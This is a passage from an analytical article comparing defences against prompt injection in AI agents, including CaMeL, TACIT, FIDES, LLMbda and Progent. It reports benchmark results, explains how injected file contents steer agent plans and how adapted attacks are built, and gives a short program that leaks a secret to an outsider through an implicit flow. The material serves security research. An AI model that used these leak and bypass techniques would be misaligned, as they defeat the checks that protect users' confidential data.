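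Odersky and colleagues quote results by domain for the two models on which they tested TACIT:

| | User tasks completed, Gemini 2.5 Pro | User tasks completed, o4-mini-high |
|---|---|---|
| Banking | 52.8% | 62.5% |
| Workspace | 53.8% | 81.4% |
| Slack | 48.6% | 68.6% |
| Travel | 1.4% | 74.3% |

One attack succeeded, in banking with o4-mini-high.

The 1.4% is 2 of the 140 travel pairs, and Odersky and colleagues don't explain it. CaMeL's design can't have made these tasks impossible, since o4-mini-high completed 74.3% of the same pairs. Gemini may have been bad at writing plans for the travel tools, or something may have gone wrong in the runs. Either way, the figure is poor evidence of how run-time checks affect task completion. CaMeL completed more tasks than TACIT in six of the other seven combinations of model and domain. Odersky and colleagues also don't say whether CaMeL's policies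 were switched on, which can make a big difference.

Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026) reran CaMeL on the banking tasks with newer models. They report the results in *AI Agents, Conversations, and Information Flow*, a version of their paper on the LLMbda calculus. With policies off, CaMeL completed 32 of 48 runs with GPT-5.2 and 34 of 48 with MiMo-v2.5. With policies on, it completed 18 of 48 with each. Many banking tasks require the agent to act on a value from an untrusted file, and strict policies forbid that.

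Even with the policies off, only 5 of 622 completed attack runs succeeded, compared with none of 588 with them on. In 97 of the 144 banking pairs, the attack needs a tool call or file that a plan for the user's task alone would never contain, so writing the plan first is normally enough to stop it. The exception was a task that told the agent to follow the instructions in a file. The privileged model wrote a loop with a branch for every tool, so the file's contents determined the actions. Without policies, such a plan gives the attacker as much control as an agent that reads the file directly.

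### What a compiler knows and what an interpreter knows

A compiler checks every branch of a program before any of it runs, and its result holds for all inputs, whereas an interpreter checks only the branches that a particular run takes. Odersky and colleagues argue that only a type system can express local purity, the guarantee that a piece of code has no effects. A run-time monitor can get a similar result by blocking all outside actions while code handles secret data, but it detects a violation only when the code attempts one.

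In exchange, the interpreter can check actual values. Enforcing a rule that payments must stay below 500 euros takes one comparison at run time, whereas a compiler would need refinement types and a proof. The typed systems TACIT and ELBA also check file paths at run time. Odersky and colleagues call the two approaches complementary and suggest adding run-time checks such as rate limits and audit logs to TACIT's library.

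CaMeL's labels don't show whether a value is correct. A false total on an invoice gets the same label as a correct one, so CaMeL's policy can only reject both, accept both or ask the user.

### When a check fails late

Suppose a plan emails the summary to Alice and then tries to post it on a public website. CaMeL's interpreter blocks the second action, but by then Alice has the email. If the privileged model writes a new plan that starts from the beginning, she may get it twice. With LACUNA, neither action would have happened if the compiler had found the violation.

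Garby and colleagues reduce the problem in their own agent, Randori, by first running the plan in a simulated world, where a failed attempt does no damage. Randori rewrites the plan until it works there, then runs it for real. However, the simulated run doesn't trigger the information-flow checks, so a plan can pass it and still fail in the middle of the real run.

FIDES, the agent that *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* describes, returns a message to the model when it blocks a call, so the model can try something else without repeating the whole task. The model chooses one call at a time, so a compiler has no finished program to check in advance.

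### Restrictions on the language

CaMeL's version of Python has no user-defined or recursive functions, while TACIT's agents can write both. Odersky and colleagues present this as a fundamental advantage of types. They argue that lifting CaMeL's restriction while still giving guarantees ahead of time would require a precise analysis of how functions flow through a program. The standard form of that analysis is EXPTIME-complete, meaning that its worst-case running time grows exponentially. Capture checking avoids this analysis because each function's type already lists what the function may use.

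The argument is sound, but it applies only when guarantees are needed before the program runs. A run-time monitor can attach labels as the program runs. The LLMbda calculus does this in a language with recursion, functions that take other functions as arguments, and code that a model writes during the run. Run-time checking therefore does not require CaMeL's restriction, which is specific to its interpreter.

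CaMeL also benefits from using Python, because models have been trained on so much of it. Garby and colleagues consider the novelty of their language a handicap for Randori, and the agents in LACUNA had similar trouble with Scala.

### Writing the policies

Whoever deploys such a system has to specify what each tool may do with labelled data. *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* (2026) describes two general rules that cover many cases. A tool with serious consequences may run only if no untrusted data influenced the call. A tool that sends data out may run under the same condition, or if every recipient is allowed to read the data. The "no untrusted data" condition lets a user send a contract to an outside lawyer who isn't on the list of readers. If the model has read nothing untrusted, the instruction presumably came from the user.

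Labels are harder than rules because somebody has to decide which label each piece of data starts with. An email's sender and recipients are a reasonable list of allowed readers, but it is less obvious which data to trust. In the FIDES experiments, the researchers marked a field as untrusted if at least one AgentDojo attack used it, but an operator has no list of future attacks. Narisetty and colleagues report that the deployed form of FIDES treats data as trusted if someone forgets to label it, and that labels are also wrong from the start if a user pastes in a stranger's text. A forgotten capability in TACIT's library also makes the checks too permissive.

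### Do labels disappear in a conversation?

Odersky and colleagues argue that systems like CaMeL have a structural gap because a value loses its labels once it enters a model's conversation as ordinary text. TACIT avoids this by keeping classified text from ever reaching the agent's model.

FIDES is a counterexample, because it labels the conversation itself. If its planning model reads the contract directly, the conversation takes on the contract's label, and so does everything the model writes afterwards, since nobody can tell which words of a reply depend on which words of the input. A web search with prices in the query then fails, because the search engine isn't among the permitted readers. A payment also fails, because the conversation now contains untrusted text. TACIT has no equivalent of this second check, so its compiler treats the next snippet the same way whether or not the agent's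 model has read a hostile line on a web page.

Labels can therefore survive in a conversation, but they become very coarse. One untrusted email is enough to block most later actions, including harmless ones. The FIDES researchers measured the cost with GPT-4o, an older model, in runs without an attack:

| | Basic agent, no policies | Basic agent, policies on labelled conversation | FIDES with policies |
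|---|---|---|---|
| Workspace | 75.0% | 37.0% | 59.0% |
| Travel | 70.0% | 73.0% | 41.0% |
| Banking | 98.8% | 37.5% | 52.5% |
| Slack | 93.3% | 20.0% | 47.6% |

FIDES recovers part of the loss by hiding data. If part of a tool result would make the conversation's label more restrictive, FIDES stores that part in a variable and shows the model only the variable's name. The model can pass the variable to another tool or have a quarantined model process it. The rest of the result, such as the date of an email with an untrusted body, stays visible.

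Travel was the exception. Most of the travel tools may run after the agent has read untrusted text, as long as no confidential data leaves, so the basic agent lost nothing. FIDES's model, however, often handled variables badly. With OpenAI's o1, a stronger model, FIDES completed 68% of the travel tasks.

Hiding data also stops many attacks by itself. Without policies, 152 injections succeeded against the basic agent and 21 against FIDES. With policies, none succeeded against either agent, after the researchers excluded some runs that AgentDojo counted as successes. The policy had blocked the agent's action in some of these runs and permitted it in others.

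*Confuse the Model, Control the Flow* (Shim, Karim and colleagues, 2026) presents FlowSeal, which also labels the agent's context, to protect private records from people who talk to the agent. To avoid blocking every message after the agent has read a record, FlowSeal uses a separate model to check whether the message reveals anything from the records. It kept 72.4% utility, compared with 75.9% for the best of the other defences, and leaked at most 3.3% of the sensitive items. But its guarantee holds only if the separate model judges correctly, and the paper's threat model excludes prompt injection.

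Odersky and colleagues are right about how CaMeL handles failed plans. When a plan fails, ordinary Python code outside the interpreter sends the error message back to the privileged model to get a new plan. The new plan depends on data from the failed run, but it starts without labels. CaMeL removes sensitive parts from these messages, but there is no formal guarantee that this is enough.

### Leaks through the branch not taken

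Garby and colleagues found a more basic flaw in CaMeL's labels, an instance of a problem that Fenton described in 1974. In the following program, `penalty` is secret and records whether the contract has a penalty clause:

```
tmp = True
leak = True
if penalty: tmp = False
if tmp: leak = False
if leak: send_email(outsider, "yes")
```

CaMeL would block an email sent directly inside `if penalty`, because the decision to send it depends on a secret. Here the decision passes through two other variables, `tmp` and `leak`. If there is a penalty clause, the program sets `tmp` to false and CaMeL labels it secret. The next line is then skipped, so `leak` stays true and keeps its public label, and the email goes out. If there is no penalty clause, `tmp` stays public and true, `leak` becomes false, and no email is sent. The outsider can tell whether there is a penalty clause by whether the email arrives,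 because CaMeL doesn't label `leak` secret when the assignment to it is skipped.

A compiler can avoid this by examining both branches. In TACIT, a program can test a classified value only inside a pure function, which can't change `tmp`.

This leak matters less under CaMeL's assumptions. Its privileged model writes the plan from the user's request alone, so the hostile line can't make it write such a program. TACIT's designers assume that the model may be working for the attacker, and CaMeL's guarantee fails under that assumption. Garby and colleagues also mention a flaw that could affect plans even when the model isn't working for the attacker. Python programs very often insert values into string literals, and CaMeL's interpreter treats an untrusted value inserted this way as trusted.

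According to Narisetty and colleagues, the CaMeL developers' own paper demonstrates two leaks, one through indirect dependencies and one through errors that an attacker triggers, and concludes that CaMeL is vulnerable to side channels.

FIDES deliberately excludes such leaks from its guarantee, which is explicit secrecy: for any fixed sequence of actions, the publicly visible effects don't depend on secret data, though the agent's choice of sequence may. If an agent refreshes a public page only when the contract has a penalty clause, the page's owner can learn about the clause. The researchers consider a stronger guarantee impractical because it would forbid almost any public action after the agent has read a secret.

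### What the LLMbda calculus guarantees

The LLMbda calculus labels values, decisions and conversations. A model's reply inherits the label of the conversation it came from, and so does any code in the reply. Programs can copy a conversation temporarily or clear it, so they can quarantine a model by querying it in a cleared copy.

To close the leak above, LLMbda stops a program that is about to change a public conversation because of a secret. The rule covers only conversations because a program can't modify anything else. Stopping also reveals information, since an observer may notice that the program didn't finish. Garby and colleagues accept this leak of up to one bit per run. CaMeL's leak is worse because its retry loop is untracked, and an attacker who can make the program run repeatedly could extract a whole secret bit by bit.

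The theorem compares two runs that differ only in data an observer may not see. Because models answer at random, each run has a probability for every visible outcome, and whatever is missing from 1 is the probability that the run never finishes. Call the two sets of probabilities μ and ν. The theorem states that some third set ω exists with

μ(q) ≤ ω(q) and ν(q) ≤ ω(q) for every outcome q, and Σ ω(q) ≤ 1.

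If an agent always answers "yes" for one secret and always "no" for another, ω must give each answer a probability of 1. The total is 2, so the theorem rules this out. Now suppose the agent answers "yes" 60% of the time for the first secret, answers "yes" 50% and "no" 30% of the time for the second, and otherwise never finishes. Then ω can be 60% for "yes" and 30% for "no", a total of 90%, which the theorem allows. The two sets of probabilities can differ by no more than the average chance of not finishing, here 30%. If the agent always finishes, they must be identical.

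This holds for every program in the language, including one written by a model under an attacker's control. The proof assistant Lean has checked the proof. Garby and colleagues also proved that the interpreter they run matches the mathematical definition, assuming the model's replies follow a fixed probability distribution.

The theorem depends on correct labels and on tools that check them. It covers only data and tools inside the program. The bank in the experiments was a simulation written in LLMbda, but a real bank's software would be outside the proof.

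A second theorem covers endorsement, LLMbda's name for explicit exceptions that let a program trust a piece of untrusted data. Endorsement can't expose secrets, but it can let a false account number through. With Qwen3.7-plus, Randori completed 36 of 48 banking runs with endorsement and 30 without it. With MiMo-v2.5, it completed 31 with endorsement and 26 without. All four results are higher than CaMeL's 18 with policies on. However, Randori enforces only some of CaMeL's policies, and the margins of error are wide because there were only 16 tasks, each run three times.

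### Attackers who adapt

Almost all of these results come from AgentDojo's stock attacks. Narisetty and colleagues warn that defences based on training or filtering the model once looked just as good. When other researchers adapted their attacks to twelve such defences, the attacks succeeded more than 90% of the time against most of them.

Narisetty and colleagues therefore ran an adaptive test on Progent, which checks each tool call against rules about tools and their arguments. The check itself is deterministic, but a language model writes the rules and may relax them during a task, and the adapted attack targeted that model. The agent ran on Qwen2.5-7B, a small open-weight model, with eight user tasks from each of three AgentDojo domains. Averaged over the domains and three repetitions:

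| | Attacks succeeded | Tasks completed under attack |
|---|---|---|
| No defence | 25.8% | 45.2% |
| Progent, stock attack | 4.2% | 27.1% |
| Progent, adapted attack | 2.6% | 25.8% |

The adapted attack did worse than the stock one. Narisetty and colleagues suspect that its wording also made the agent less likely to obey it, so the result may reflect a weak attack as much as a strong defence. They tried only one kind of adapted attack. In the workspace domain, no attack succeeded even without a defence, so only banking and Slack provide evidence. Progent also needed about 15 times as many model calls per task. The researchers work for a company that sells agent security tools, and the study has not been peer-reviewed.

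The result fits *AutoDojo*, where some defences that restrict the system around the model also withstood adapted attacks. Progent's developers report success rates of 0.5% to 4.2% for attacks adapted to their system. Narisetty and colleagues leave testing CaMeL against adapted attacks for future work. They cite a newer benchmark, AgentDyn, which tested CaMeL and Progent on more open-ended tasks and found that such defences often block legitimate work.

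The ELBA experiment with hijacked sub-agents avoided the problem of weak attacks by assuming that every injection takes over the sub-agent that reads it. But it too used stock injections rather than ones adapted to the policies.

### Why sandboxes are still useful

A sandbox, such as a container, works with any programming language and needs no labels or special types. The coding agents Claude Code and OpenCode can run a model's code in one.

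Unlike TACIT and CaMeL, a sandbox doesn't follow individual values inside the program, so it can't stop data leaking from one permitted operation to another. An operator could keep the contracts in one sandbox and allow network access only in a second. But the assistant usually has to pass something from the first to the second, and somebody then has to decide what it may pass.

The developers of TACIT and ELBA nevertheless favour a sandbox in addition to types. A bug in the Scala compiler, the Java virtual machine or CaMeL's interpreter could let a program bypass every rule about values. The operating system enforces the sandbox separately, so the attacker would need a second bug to escape it. Sandboxes also cover code the other checks never examine, such as the commands `make` runs. In a sandbox without network access, those commands can't upload the contract.
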